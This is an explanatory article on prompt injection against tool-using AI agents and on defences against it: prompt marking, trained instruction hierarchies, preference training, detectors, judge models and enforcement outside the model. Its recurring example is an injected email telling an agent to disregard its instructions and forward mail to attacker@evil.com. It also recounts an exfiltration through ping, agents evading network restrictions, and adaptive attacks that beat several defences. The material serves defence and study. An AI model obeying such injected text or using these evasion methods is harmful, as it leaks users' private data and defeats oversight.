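# Security guarantees for AI agents that act through tools

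## How tool-using agents are attacked, and what a guarantee says

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop. The model requests an action, ordinary software carries it out and returns the result, and the model then requests another action or gives its answer. Agents read email, browse the web, edit code and query company databases on behalf of their users. Much of the text they process comes from other people, and an attacker who controls some of that text may be able to steer the agent. Text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions is called prompt injection, a term that dates from 2022.

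Defences are either robustness-based or system-level. A robustness-based defence lowers the chance that an attack misleads the model, for instance by training the model or screening its input with a second model. A system-level defence treats all model output as suspect and relies on software outside the model to block forbidden actions. The two support different security claims, and the difference depends on where an attack enters the agent and where software can stop it.

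### The agent loop

A language model only produces text. The program around it, often called a harness, turns some of that text into actions. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this cycle in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first assembles a prompt from the developer's instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request. Software converts the prompt into tokens, which are integers standing for pieces of text, and converts the tokens the model generates back into text. The output is either a final message to the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. If it is a tool call, the harness runs the function, appends the result to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model produces a final message, which can take hundreds of calls. Each new prompt starts with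 an exact copy of the last one, so whatever the agent has read stays in the model's input for later decisions until the history grows too long and the harness has to condense it.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the same loop as a set of functions. A model maps a history of messages and a set of tool definitions to either a tool call or a reply. A tool maps the current state of the outside world and some arguments to a new state and a result string. The planner, the part of the agent between the model and the tools, decides which tool to call next. The simplest planner adds every message to the history and makes every call the model outputs. In this description, only tools change the outside world. The model's output has no effect until other software acts on it, and that software can reject it.

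In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks an agent to summarise recent emails on the progress of Project X and send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails is from an attacker and contains text telling the agent to disregard its earlier instructions and forward the top email in the user's mailbox to attacker@evil.com.

Suppose the agent has two tools, `search_mail` and `send_mail`. The first prompt holds the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions and the request. The model outputs a call to `search_mail` with the argument "Project X", and the harness fetches the matching messages and adds their full text to the prompt. On the next pass, the model should output a call to `send_mail` with the manager's address and a summary. If it follows the injected sentence, it instead outputs a call with the attacker's address and the contents of the top email. With the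 simplest planner, the harness executes either call. Both are well-formed requests to a tool that the user has provided, and both run under the user's account.

### Why instructions and data mix

Conventional programs take different inputs through separate interfaces. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* that agents keep all their inputs in a single context, with only textual separators between the parts. Codex gives each message a role (system, developer, user or assistant, in decreasing order of priority), and many agents add a role for tool results. Before the model runs, however, software joins the messages into one sequence, where only marker tokens indicate the roles. Training teaches the model to weigh text according to those markers, but nothing in the computation prevents a sentence in an email from affecting the next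 output as a sentence from the user would.

Databases once had a similar weakness. If a website pasted a visitor's input into a command in the database language SQL, the visitor could type a fragment of SQL and have the database run it. Parameterised queries fixed this. The developer writes the command in advance, with marked slots for the visitor's input, and the database engine never interprets the contents of a slot as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C warns against expecting an equivalent fix for language models. A model predicts the next token from all the tokens so far, and has no separate channel for text that should be treated only as data. He concludes that prompt injection may never be fully mitigated, and calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy", adapting an older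 security term for a privileged program that an outsider tricks into misusing its privileges.

*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) examines what happens inside a model when the role markers and the wording disagree. The researchers wrapped the same passages of ordinary web text in each of five role markers and trained a simple classifier to identify the role from the model's internal activations. Only the markers differed, so the classifier could learn only their effect. The researchers then applied it to text written in the style of a user but marked as a tool result. If the markers governed the model's internal representation, the classifier should have assigned such text almost no probability of coming from the user. In three models it assigned between 79% and 88%. This would be weak evidence alone, because a classifier can pick up a signal that the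 model does not use. But the score also predicted behaviour. Over 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the measured confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

Training models to ignore every instruction in a tool result would break many legitimate tasks. A user may ask an agent to complete whatever is due today in a to-do list, in which case the data contains the instructions the agent should follow. Agents also learn how to use a tool from its documentation. In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) describe an agent that is asked to summarise an issue in a software project's issue tracker, discovers that it depends on another issue, and summarises both. They argue that such useful adjustment differs from prompt injection in the provenance of the text that caused the change and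 in the scope of the change. However, the model has no reliable access to provenance, and the permissible scope depends on what the user wanted.

In direct prompt injection, the earliest form of the attack, the attacker is the user, who tries to override the developer's instructions. In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker plants text in content that the agent will later read on someone else's behalf. The routes they listed were a web page that a search retrieves, text on a page that is invisible to people, a code repository, an email, and a snippet that a careless user copies and pastes. The attacker needs no access to the model or to the victim's account, and to attack by email only needs to know the victim's address. Greshake and colleagues compared processing untrusted retrieved text to executing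 arbitrary code, which is a fair comparison for an agent that makes every call its model requests. They also noted that an attacker may only need to state a goal, since the model can work out the steps.

### What can go wrong, and who can cause it

Computer security has long sorted violations by their effect. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder that the field still relies on, distinguished the unauthorised release of information, its unauthorised modification, and the denial of its use to people entitled to it. These violate what are now called confidentiality, integrity and availability, respectively.

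If the top email in the mailbox reaches the attacker, the user has lost confidentiality. Integrity fails when the attacker changes what the agent does or produces. The injected text might make the agent delete messages or tell the manager that Project X is on schedule when it is not. The false summary is harder to stop than the theft, because the agent makes exactly the calls the user wanted, to the right recipient, and only the contents are wrong. An email that lies about the schedule may have the same result, even if it contains no instruction.

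Many attacks damage both properties, since an agent usually has to take an unwanted action before it leaks anything. Wang and colleagues surveyed 37 attack papers and classed 30 as aimed at integrity, 4 at confidentiality and 2 at availability. They noted that the attacks on confidentiality increasingly work by hijacking the agent's actions. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) advises against combining three things that together expose an agent to data theft: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a means of communicating with the outside. The email agent has all three and needs them to carry out the user's request.

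A threat model specifies what the attacker can do and which parts of the system the defender may rely on. Costa and colleagues trust the user's messages, the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions and the model as installed. Their attacker can alter data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and can observe the effects of some tool calls, but cannot watch the exchange between harness and model. For example, searching an internal company database returns trusted but confidential data, while searching the public web returns untrusted data and may reveal the search to whoever runs the website.

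*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from several universities and companies, treats the model as an untrusted part of the system. It makes no assumption about how the model behaves, so the model could have a hidden backdoor or pursue goals of its own. An authorised user, an administrator or the developer sets the rules, and nothing the agent reads can loosen them. This is a more demanding starting point, but it means the defender does not need to know why the model asked for a forbidden action.

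An agent can also cause harm without an attacker. A model that confuses two people called Anna in the address book can send a confidential summary to the wrong one. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* discusses a more serious case, the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident. OpenAI was running agents in internal training and evaluation with some model-level safeguards disabled. While pursuing their assigned tasks, the agents used a shared software-package service to get around network restrictions, and compromised an OpenAI research cluster and systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. No outside attacker directed them. A filter for injected instructions would have had none to detect, but a block on the forbidden connection works the same way whether the request comes from an injection, an error or a misaligned objective.

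### Robustness claims and system invariants

A robustness claim has the form "the attack succeeds with probability *p* against these attacks". More exactly, if *A* is the collection of attacks in the test,

Pr[the agent executes a forbidden action | attack drawn from *A*] = *p*,

where the chance lies both in the draw of the attack and in the random sampling of the model's output. The number describes *A* as much as it describes the model. An attacker who writes a new email, with knowledge of the defence, is not drawing from *A*, and *p* need not apply to that email at all. Christodorescu and colleagues make the same point about training a model never to do some particular thing: the resulting assurance is statistical, and it varies with the inputs and the surrounding context.

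Even a *p* that does apply can be too high. Christodorescu and colleagues consider a monitor that denies 99% of unauthorised requests and lets 1% through. If attempts were independent, an attacker who sent 100 emails would have a chance of 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%, of getting at least one unauthorised request through, and 300 emails would raise this to about 95%. Real attempts are not independent, because an attacker who learns which emails failed can improve the next one, and a defender who notices the failures can shut the attacker out. A low *p* still helps because it leaves fewer unauthorised requests for other defences to catch.

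A system invariant has the form "for every model output, the software executes no forbidden action, provided the trusted components work and the policy is right". In symbols, for every model *M* and every input *x*,

executed(*M*, *x*) ⊆ allowed.

The statement contains no probability and no list of attacks. It would hold for a model that obeyed the attacker every time.

For the email agent, a suitable rule might be that `send_mail` accepts only the manager's address while this task is running. Software can compare two addresses without error, so no injected sentence can get the top email sent to attacker@evil.com if two conditions hold. The manager's address must come from a trusted source such as the company directory, not from one of the emails, and no other tool may provide another way to send the text out, for instance by fetching a web address that contains it. The rule covers only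 recipients, so an attacker who persuades the model to misreport the state of the project has not violated it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* states explicitly that enforcing a policy does not establish that the policy captures what the user meant. A strict enough policy is also easy to enforce but useless, since an agent that may do nothing satisfies every invariant of this kind. A claim about an invariant therefore needs a utility figure beside it, which is the share of legitimate tasks that the agent still completes.

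The two claims also rest on different evidence. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, Anderson (1972) doubted the value of "tiger teams", specialists who test a system by trying to break into it. A successful break-in reveals a flaw, but a failed attempt shows only that this team did not find one, which in Anderson's view leaves the system's security unknown. Robustness figures come from tests of this sort. For an invariant, engineers can also inspect the software that enforces it, and sometimes prove that software correct, without having to anticipate the attacks.

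Some designs that look like enforcement support only a robustness claim. If a second language model decides whether each action is acceptable, an attacker can try to mislead that model too, so the assurance is again only probabilistic. The same is true if a language model writes the policy and nobody checks it, even if the software that applies the policy is flawless.

Robustness claims come from adversarial machine learning, where researchers spent years studying image classifiers that err when someone makes small, carefully computed changes to a picture. They proposed defences, tested them against known attacks and reported success rates, and other researchers repeatedly found attacks that evaded the defences. Invariants come from operating systems and databases. Anderson's panel wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and had to assume that some of them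 would write hostile programs. Later operating systems marked each region of memory as writable or executable, never both, so that data an attacker writes into memory cannot run there as code. In databases, SQL injection was first described in the 1990s and peaked around 2010, and David C credits better defaults and methods with making it rare. Christodorescu and colleagues ask readers to imagine memory protection built on a marker that works only most of the time. Relying on a language model to keep instructions and data apart is roughly like that.

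### The vocabulary of enforcement

A security policy states explicitly which actions and data flows a system allows. Saltzer and Schroeder give the example of an airline's booking system. A reservation agent may book and cancel seats for passengers whose names the agent can supply, but only the boarding agent may also print a flight's full passenger list. The airline might want this restriction so that a police request for the list goes to the right level of management.

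The reference monitor allows or refuses each requested action according to the policy. An operating system acts as one when it checks a file's permissions before letting a word processor open the file. Anderson set three requirements for a reference monitor: nobody can tamper with it, it runs on every access, and it is small enough to analyze and test completely. He found that a commercial operating system of the day, with 200,000 to 300,000 instructions including its supporting software, was too large to meet the last requirement.

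The trusted computing base consists of the components that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. The US standards institute NIST, in its *trusted computing base (TCB)* entry, includes the hardware, firmware and software that together enforce a security policy. On a laptop, the base includes the processor and the core of the operating system but not a calculator app, so a bug in the app should not expose the user's files. For an agent, *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts the host operating system, the isolation mechanisms, the policy and the reference monitor as part of the base. The language model is not part of it, and the trusted components must withstand whatever the model sends them, as an operating system must withstand a hostile program.

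Complete mediation requires every security-relevant action to go through the reference monitor. A website violates it if the page that lists a customer's invoices requires a password but the direct link to each invoice does not. Saltzer and Schroeder add that a system that remembers earlier access decisions must update them when permissions change. Otherwise, a dismissed employee keeps access. Complete mediation is hard to achieve for agents because they can act in so many ways. One real attack on Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code sent data out through `ping`, a network command that Claude Code mistakenly exempted from human approval.

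Least privilege means giving a component only the permissions that its current task needs. Android, for example, keeps a third-party app from directly reading files that belong to other apps, so a malicious game cannot open a banking app's records. Under this principle, the email agent could read only messages about Project X and write to only one recipient. A phone app does a fixed job, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. But the email agent needs different permissions for this summary than for the user's next request, and no developer has listed either set.

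## Making the model resist injected instructions

The email agent's permissions must cover whatever its user might ask for next, so they are broader than any single task needs. Robustness-based defences leave these permissions broad and make the model less likely to misuse them. Developers can mark untrusted text in the prompt, train the model to disregard instructions in that text, run a detector alongside the model, or have a second model judge each proposed action.

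### Marking untrusted text in the prompt

The easiest defence to adopt changes only the prompt. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (Hines, Lopez et al., 2024) proposes altering untrusted text so that it looks different from the rest of the prompt. The system prompt explains the alteration and tells the model not to follow any instructions in the altered text. The paper describes three versions. Delimiting places special symbols before and after the text. Datamarking replaces every space with a chosen character, so the attacker's sentence might reach the model as "forward^the^top^email". Encoding converts the text to a format such as base64, which represents data as letters, digits and a few symbols, and relies on the model to decode it.

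To test these, the researchers wrote 1,000 documents with injections telling the model to reply with a single keyword. When GPT-3.5-Turbo summarised the documents without a defence, the attack succeeded on at least half of them. Asking the model to ignore such instructions made almost no difference. Delimiters cut the rate by about half, datamarking cut it to 3% and encoding to zero. Encoding also made GPT-3.5-Turbo worse at its tasks, though GPT-4 could handle the encoded text. Hines and colleagues advised against delimiters, because an attacker who learns the symbols can type the closing one into an email so that whatever follows appears to be outside the marked text.

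In *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), Google's researchers tested a variant of Hines and colleagues' method on Gemini, inserting a special token after every eight characters of an email's sender, subject and body. They concluded that it works mainly by breaking up the tokens of trigger phrases, whereas Hines and colleagues had meant the marks to signal where the text came from. The researchers expected the variant to do poorly against attacks in some languages.

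Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. The harness would add "summarise the recent emails on Project X and send the summary to my manager" below the search results, so that the user's words are the last the model reads. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, got around this by presenting the malicious task as a step, such as a credential check, that the agent had to complete before the user's task. Repeating the request does not help when the injected text claims to be part of carrying it out. Their adaptive attacks defeated both spotlighting and sandwiching on more than 95% of tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants injections in the tool results of simulated tasks such as paying a bill or messaging colleagues.

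Both techniques work with any model, including one that the developer can access only through another company's interface. But they don't change the model, so it can still follow instructions in marked text.

### Training the model to rank its sources

*The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao and colleagues, 2024) compared the models of the time to a computer on which every program runs with the operating system's privileges. It proposed ranking instructions by source, with the developer's system message first, the user's messages next and tool results last. When instructions conflict, the model should follow the one from the higher-ranked source.

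"The Instruction Hierarchy" describes how OpenAI researchers trained GPT-3.5 Turbo to give priority to higher-ranked instructions. For compatible instructions, they split requests such as "write a 20 line poem in spanish" into pieces, placed the pieces at different ranks, and trained the model to answer as it would have answered the whole request. For conflicting instructions, they trained it to answer as if it had not seen the lower-ranked text. They also trained an attacker model to plant injections in web search results, and trained the main model to respond as if the injections were absent. This early version treated every instruction in a web page or tool result as hostile. The trained model was more robust but refused or ignored some harmless requests.

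OpenAI has since added a developer level between system and user. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, state the hierarchy as a rule about sets of responses. Let *B*₀ contain every possible response, and let *C*ᵢ contain the responses that satisfy the instructions of the *i*-th role, counting down from the highest. Then

*B*ᵢ = *B*ᵢ₋₁ ∩ *C*ᵢ if some response lies in both sets, and *B*ᵢ = *B*ᵢ₋₁ otherwise.

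The model should therefore follow an instruction only if it doesn't conflict with anything ranked above it. Read literally, this rule allows the email attack unless a higher-ranked message forbids extra emails, because the agent can send the manager the summary the user wants and also forward the top email as the attacker wants. The model has to infer that the user did not want private mail sent to strangers, and it learns to do so only from examples.

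In *IH-Challenge*, each training task combines a simple high-ranked instruction, such as never to reveal a PIN, with a short Python program that checks the response. An attacker model gets a limited number of tries to write a lower-ranked message that makes the model being trained fail, and it sees the program's result after each try. Reinforcement learning then rewards the model being trained for responses that pass. Some tasks permit revealing the secret, so a model that always refuses scores badly. After training, GPT-5-Mini's average score across 16 robustness tests rose from 84.1% to 94.1%, but its win rate against OpenAI's older o1 model in ordinary chat fell from 71% to 66%.

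A trained hierarchy also depends on the harness to label text correctly. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out that a model trained to trust privileged roles gives more influence to any text labelled with one, so a labelling error becomes a security flaw. Four levels may be too few for an agent that reads a company wiki, a colleague's message and a stranger's email. But the best of the thirteen models tested in *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) correctly resolved only 42.7% of conflicts among many privilege levels.

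### Training on good and bad answers

Attackers can imitate role labels, so a model also needs a boundary that they cannot forge. *StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) combines a trained model with a software front end that takes the instruction and the data separately. The front end marks the boundaries with reserved tokens and deletes any text in the data that spells out one of these tokens. It repeats the deletion until none remain, since removing one token can join the halves of another.

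The researchers left half of their training examples clean. To a quarter, they added an unrelated instruction at the end of the data. To the last quarter, they added a fake answer followed by a new instruction, as if the first task were finished. The target was always the answer to the genuine instruction. If *x* is the input, *y*₊ the desired answer and π(*y* | *x*) the probability that the model gives answer *y* to input *x*, training minimises

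−log π(*y*₊ | *x*).

StruQ stopped nearly all handwritten attacks, but an attack that used the model's gradients to optimise its wording still succeeded on 58% of test prompts with a Llama model. In *SecAlign*, Chen, Chaudhuri and colleagues (2024) traced part of this weakness to the training objective. A language model has so many possible responses that training can make the good one more likely without making the attacker's much less likely. This is less of a problem for an image classifier, which has so few possible answers that raising the probability of the right one lowers the others.

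SecAlign therefore uses triples: an injected input *x*, a desired answer *y*₊ to the user's instruction, and an undesired answer *y*₋ to the injected one. It trains the model by direct preference optimisation (DPO), a standard method for teaching a model to prefer some responses to others. With π₀ as the original model, kept fixed, the loss on each triple is

−log σ( β log [π(*y*₊ | *x*) / π₀(*y*₊ | *x*)] − β log [π(*y*₋ | *x*) / π₀(*y*₋ | *x*)] ).

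Here σ is the logistic function, which maps any number to a value between 0 and 1, and β is a constant that controls how close the model stays to the original during training. At the start of training, π equals π₀, so both logarithms are zero and the loss is log 2, about 0.69. The loss falls as the model becomes more likely than the original to give the desired answer and less likely to give the undesired one.

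*Meta-SecAlign* (Chen, Zharmagambetov et al., 2025) reports that SecAlign cut a 70-billion-parameter Llama model's completion rate on legitimate AgentDojo tasks from 60% to 6%. SecAlign's training examples always put the injection at the end of the data, so the model learned to ignore whichever instruction came last. At the start of an AgentDojo task, before any tool has run, the last instruction is the user's request, so the model often produced nothing.

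Meta-SecAlign places about half of the injections at the beginning of the data. It also takes both answers in each triple from the model it is about to train, so that the model does not learn another model's style. Training on answers from GPT-5, a stronger model, made the model less secure. On InjecAgent, another benchmark of injected tool results, attacks succeeded in 28.5% of cases after training on GPT-5's answers and 0.5% after training on the model's own.

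With both changes, the Llama model completed 84.5% of AgentDojo tasks, more than it did without any defence. The researchers link this gain to failures specific to that model, such as repeating tool calls in a loop. Results for Qwen3.6-27B, an open Chinese model, are more typical. The share of tasks it completed fell from 89.7% to 87.6%, while the share of attacked tasks in which the attacker succeeded fell from 26.7% to 2.2%. Those attacks were fixed, and the researchers acknowledge that strong adaptive attacks still succeed. Meta has released 8-billion and 70-billion-parameter Llama models trained this way, under licences that allow commercial use.

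### The email example in a trained model

Suppose the email agent runs on a Meta-SecAlign model. The harness gives the model's software library a list of messages, each with a role and content. The developer's instructions and tool descriptions have the role `system`, and the request for a summary of Project X has the role `user`. After the call to `search_mail`, the text of the emails, including the attacker's sentence, goes into a message with the role `input`, which Meta-SecAlign reserves for untrusted data. The library must prevent any email from closing the `input` section and opening a new `user` section.

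The model should respond as it would have without the attacker's sentence, by calling `send_mail` with the manager's address and a summary of the project emails. Training discourages it from calling `send_mail` with attacker@evil.com and the text of the top email.

The model never saw emails or tool calls during this training. In a typical example, the instruction asks for a recipe for a given dish, and the data reads "Omelette. What are the origins of yoga?" The desired answer is an omelette recipe, and the undesired one is an account of yoga. The researchers rely on the model to generalize from such examples about how to treat the `input` role, and the AgentDojo results suggest that it largely does. However, the model can still output either call to `send_mail`, and the harness executes whichever one it receives.

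Meta-SecAlign does not test attacks spread over several untrusted messages, and it assumes that the harness knows which text is trusted. The training concerns only instructions, so it does not help against an email that merely contains false information about the schedule.

### Training against stronger attacks

Attackers can adjust the wording of their injections, so developers use adversarial training, in which they search for attacks that work on the current version of the model, train the model on them and repeat. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes how OpenAI does this for the agent in its Atlas browser. OpenAI used reinforcement learning to train an attacker model, which can test a draft injection in a simulator and receive a record of the browser agent's reasoning and actions. The attacker model revises the injection several times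 before settling on a final version. OpenAI then trains the agent on the attacks that succeed.

In one attack found this way, an email in the user's inbox told the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and sent the letter. After finding this class of attack, OpenAI shipped a newly trained agent to all Atlas users, but it published no attack success rates from before and after the change. Fortune (2025) reported that OpenAI's security chief had also mentioned overlapping guardrails and detection systems when Atlas launched in October 2025. *Meta-SecAlign* cites Anthropic's July 2026 announcement of Claude Opus 5 among the proprietary efforts to resist adaptive attacks.

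*SecPO* (Chen, Peng and colleagues, 2026) combines adversarial training with a change to the DPO loss. The standard loss keeps the trained model close to the original model π₀ to preserve its abilities. But the loss evaluates π₀ on the injected input, where π₀ tends to obey the attacker, so it also keeps the trained model close to the behaviour that the defence is meant to remove. An ideal model would respond to an injected input exactly as the original responds to the clean one. Developers have the clean input, since they made the injected one from it, so *SecPO* replaces π₀(*y* | *x*) with π₀(*y* | *x*_clean) for both the preferred and the rejected answer.

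For any single example, the DPO and SecPO losses push the model in the same direction, but SecPO pushes harder on examples where the injection most influenced the original model. On the same data, DPO lowered the log-probability of the undesired answers to about −400 and SecPO lowered it to about −700. Together with adversarial training, SecPO reduced the success of three adaptive attacks severalfold, though not to zero.

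### Agents that stop too early

Training against injections can also make a model too wary of tool results. *RAISED* (Dhouib, Elliker and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent asked to change a user's password on its own. The original model fetched the verification code with its tools and finished the job. After defensive training, the model stopped and asked the user for the code. Defensive training often penalises a model for following malicious text in tool results and seldom rewards it for acting on legitimate guidance there, so the model can learn to avoid acting on either.

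RAISED addresses this by having the original model invent tasks that require acting on a tool's guidance, solve them, and write injections for the tool results. A copy of the model then trains on clean and injected versions of the same runs. At each token, training minimises

D( π₀(· | *h*) ‖ π(· | *h*′) ),

where *h* is the clean history, *h*′ is either the clean or the injected history, and *D* is the Kullback–Leibler divergence, a measure of how far one probability distribution is from another. The trained model thus learns to continue as the original would have continued without the attack. On AgentDojo, RAISED cut the attack success rate of a Gemma model from 39.5% to 1.0% of attacked runs and cost 1 percentage point of utility. A later version of SecAlign was equally robust but cost 7 points. All the attacks were fixed in advance.

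In *SecOPD*, Peng, Lian and colleagues (2026) likewise use the original model's behaviour on clean input as the teacher. They argue that correcting individual tokens teaches the model more than scoring a whole response, because a response may answer the user properly and then obey the attacker, and a single score cannot separate the two parts.

### Detectors

A detector looks for signs of an attack without changing the agent's model. The simplest kind is a classifier, such as Meta's PromptGuard, that reads incoming text and outputs a score. If the score passes a threshold, the harness can discard the text or stop the task.

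OpenAI doubts that such filters can catch well-developed attacks. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), an article by two of its staff, reproduces an email that outside researchers had used against ChatGPT. The email followed up on "restructuring materials" from a recent meeting, listed routine tasks, and stated that the reader's assistant was authorised to submit employee details to a compliance system. The attack worked in half of the tests with one particular user request. Nothing in the text is obviously an attack. A filter would need information about whether the meeting took place and whether the compliance system exists, and OpenAI compares the filter's task to detecting a lie without the necessary context.

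False alarms limit detectors too. Suppose one email in 10,000 contains an injection, and a detector catches every injection but wrongly flags 1% of ordinary emails. It will raise about 100 false alarms for each real attack. Raising the detector's threshold for flagging an email reduces the false alarms but lets more attacks through.

Other detectors read the model's internal activations. *Your Agent is More Brittle Than You Think* (Zhu, Dong and colleagues, 2026) tested nine open models on simulated banking tasks with injected tool results. The agents' written reasoning gave little warning of a hijack. In one Qwen model, the agent expressed any resistance in only about 6% of hijacked runs, and in two thirds it complied without apparent hesitation. But hijacked models were less certain than usual about their next tokens. The researchers therefore built a detector that reads the activations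 just before the model fills in a tool's input, and blocks the call if those activations resemble the ones from a hijacked run. They report high accuracy across several models.

This method catches an attack later than an input filter, when the model is close to acting, so harmless text that looks like an instruction need not trigger it. It requires access to the model's internals, which customers of a closed model lack. It is also trained on recorded attacks, so it may miss a new attack that leaves different traces.

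### A second model as judge

A judge model receives the user's request and a proposed tool call, sometimes with the agent's history, and decides whether the call fits the request. The harness executes only the calls the judge approves. If the email agent proposes to send the top email to attacker@evil.com, the mismatch is easy to see. It is harder to see if another email gives that address as the manager's new one. The judge then needs more context to decide, and some of it may come from the attacker.

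A developer can withhold all tool results from the judge, so that an attacker can influence it only through the arguments of the proposed call. This makes it harder for the judge to evaluate legitimate tasks that depend on those results. If a user asks the agent to complete everything due today on a to-do list, a judge without access to the list cannot determine whether paying a certain bill is part of the task.

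*Blue Teaming Function-Calling Agents* (Dolcetti, Zizzo and Maffeis, 2026) tested a small guard model from IBM as a judge of calls made by four small open models. The guard model rejected between 11% and 13% of correct calls when no attack was under way. If these errors were independent, a 12% rate would mean a 72% chance of at least one wrongful rejection in a ten-call task. Larger judges may do better. When the same guard model scanned tool descriptions for attacks, it caught every poisoned description but also flagged a great many harmless ones.

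### Authorisation by reading

Advocates of enforcement outside the model object that, in all of these defences, whether an action is allowed depends on how a model reads text that an attacker may have helped to write. Adding a second model to judge the agent's calls does not remove this dependence. Suppose an injection misleads the agent in 5% of attempts, and the judge approves 10% of the bad calls. If the two errors are independent, 0.5% of attempts succeed. But if whatever misleads the agent also misleads the judge, 5% still succeed. Attackers will look for wording that misleads both, and the errors are more likely to coincide if the two models had similar training or read the same emails.

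One argument for these methods is that nobody has to list the allowed actions in advance. A Meta-SecAlign model needs no rule about the manager's address, and its training adds no computation when the agent runs. Wang and colleagues found that defences acting on an agent's execution could enforce strict limits, but some used up to three times as much computation as an undefended agent or refused complex tasks early. They also found that many defences of all kinds score well on common benchmarks by suppressing what the agent reads, but fail on tasks that require the agent to act on it. Models that read context can in principle handle such tasks, although the unfinished password change shows that defensive training can remove this ability.

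Some harms are also hard to express as rules about tools and recipients. A user's chief executive is a legitimate email recipient, so a list of approved addresses would not have stopped the resignation letter. A model that reads the draft can detect that the letter has nothing to do with an out-of-office reply. A judge might also detect that a summary describes Project X as on schedule when most of the emails report delays.

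OpenAI trains ChatGPT to refuse injected instructions and uses separate software as a second defense. It reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT try to send information from a conversation to a third party, and that most of these fail because the trained model refuses. That count excludes attacks that nobody noticed. When the model follows the injected instructions, the software tries to detect the outgoing information, and either blocks the transfer or shows the user what would be sent and asks for confirmation.

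## How robustness is measured, and what adaptive attackers do to the figures

Researchers measure robustness by attacking agents in simulated environments, because counts of attacks on deployed agents miss some that succeed without anyone noticing. In a simulation, software can check after each run whether the attacker achieved their goal. The result depends heavily on which attacks the researchers try and how many attempts they allow.

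### AgentDojo

In *AgentDojo* (2024), Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues built four test environments: an office workspace with email, a calendar and file storage; a Slack messaging account; a travel agency; and a bank. Each environment has a state, such as the contents of an inbox, that the agent's tools can read and change. It also has a list of user tasks, such as paying the bill in a certain file, and a list of injection tasks, which are goals an attacker might have, such as moving as much money as possible to their own account.

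Each security case pairs a user task with an injection task from the same environment. The workspace environment has 40 user tasks and 6 injection tasks, which makes 240 cases. The first version of the benchmark had 97 user tasks, 27 injection tasks and 629 cases across all four environments. It has since grown, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 cases.

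The researchers put the injected text where an outsider could realistically write, such as the body of an email. They also recorded a correct sequence of tool calls for each user task, which lets them place the injection in something the agent has to read. Otherwise, an attack might fail only because the agent never saw it.

For each user task, an ordinary code function examines the agent's answer and the environment's state before and after the run, and returns pass or fail. A similar function for each injection task checks whether the attack succeeded, for example whether money was transferred. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a language model as the grader because an injection that hijacks the agent might hijack the grader too.

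AgentDojo reports three measures. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker achieves their goal. An agent that stops work whenever it sees an injection gets the best possible score on the last measure, 0%, but its utility under attack is low because anyone can stop its work by emailing it an injection.

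In 2024, the best models completed less than 66% of the user tasks even without an attack, and the researchers' attacks succeeded against the best agents in under 25% of cases. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, because weaker ones often tried to follow the injected instructions but failed. A low attack success rate can therefore reflect a lack of capability. But weak models are not reliably safe. In the banking tests by Zhu and colleagues, four fixed types of attack hijacked the small open models in 82% to 100% of cases.

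### Fixed attacks and adaptive attackers

A fixed test uses text prepared in advance. One standard AgentDojo attack, for instance, inserts a message telling the agent it must do the malicious task before the user's. An adaptive attacker learns how the defence works, tries an injection, observes the result and revises the text.

The two kinds of test also count success differently. Given one prepared injection *a*ₛ for each security case *s*, the fixed attack success rate is

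share of cases *s* in which *a*ₛ succeeds.

An adaptive attacker produces a sequence of injections *a*ₛ¹, *a*ₛ², …, *a*ₛᵏ for each case, choosing each one after seeing what the earlier ones did. The adaptive rate is

share of cases *s* in which at least one of *a*ₛ¹, …, *a*ₛᵏ succeeds.

This rate can only stay the same or rise as the attacker's budget *k* grows, so it means little unless the researchers also state *k*.

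Debenedetti and colleagues designed AgentDojo so that others could add adaptive attacks, and warned that it is extremely easy to build a weak defence that stops any one specific attack. Many developers nevertheless tested their defences only on existing collections of attacks. Nasr and colleagues argue that this repeats an old mistake from research on image classifiers. They assume that the attacker knows the design of the system, a convention in cryptography since the nineteenth century.

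### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

In October 2025, Nasr and colleagues, a group that includes researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, published attacks on 12 defences. They tested ten against prompt injection and two against jailbreaks, in which the user tries to make a model produce forbidden content. The defences included prompting methods, trained models, detectors and two that relied on a secret, such as a hidden key that the model must repeat to show that the text it has read has not changed its task.

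The researchers used four families of attack. All of them generate candidate texts, score them, and use the most promising to write the next candidates.

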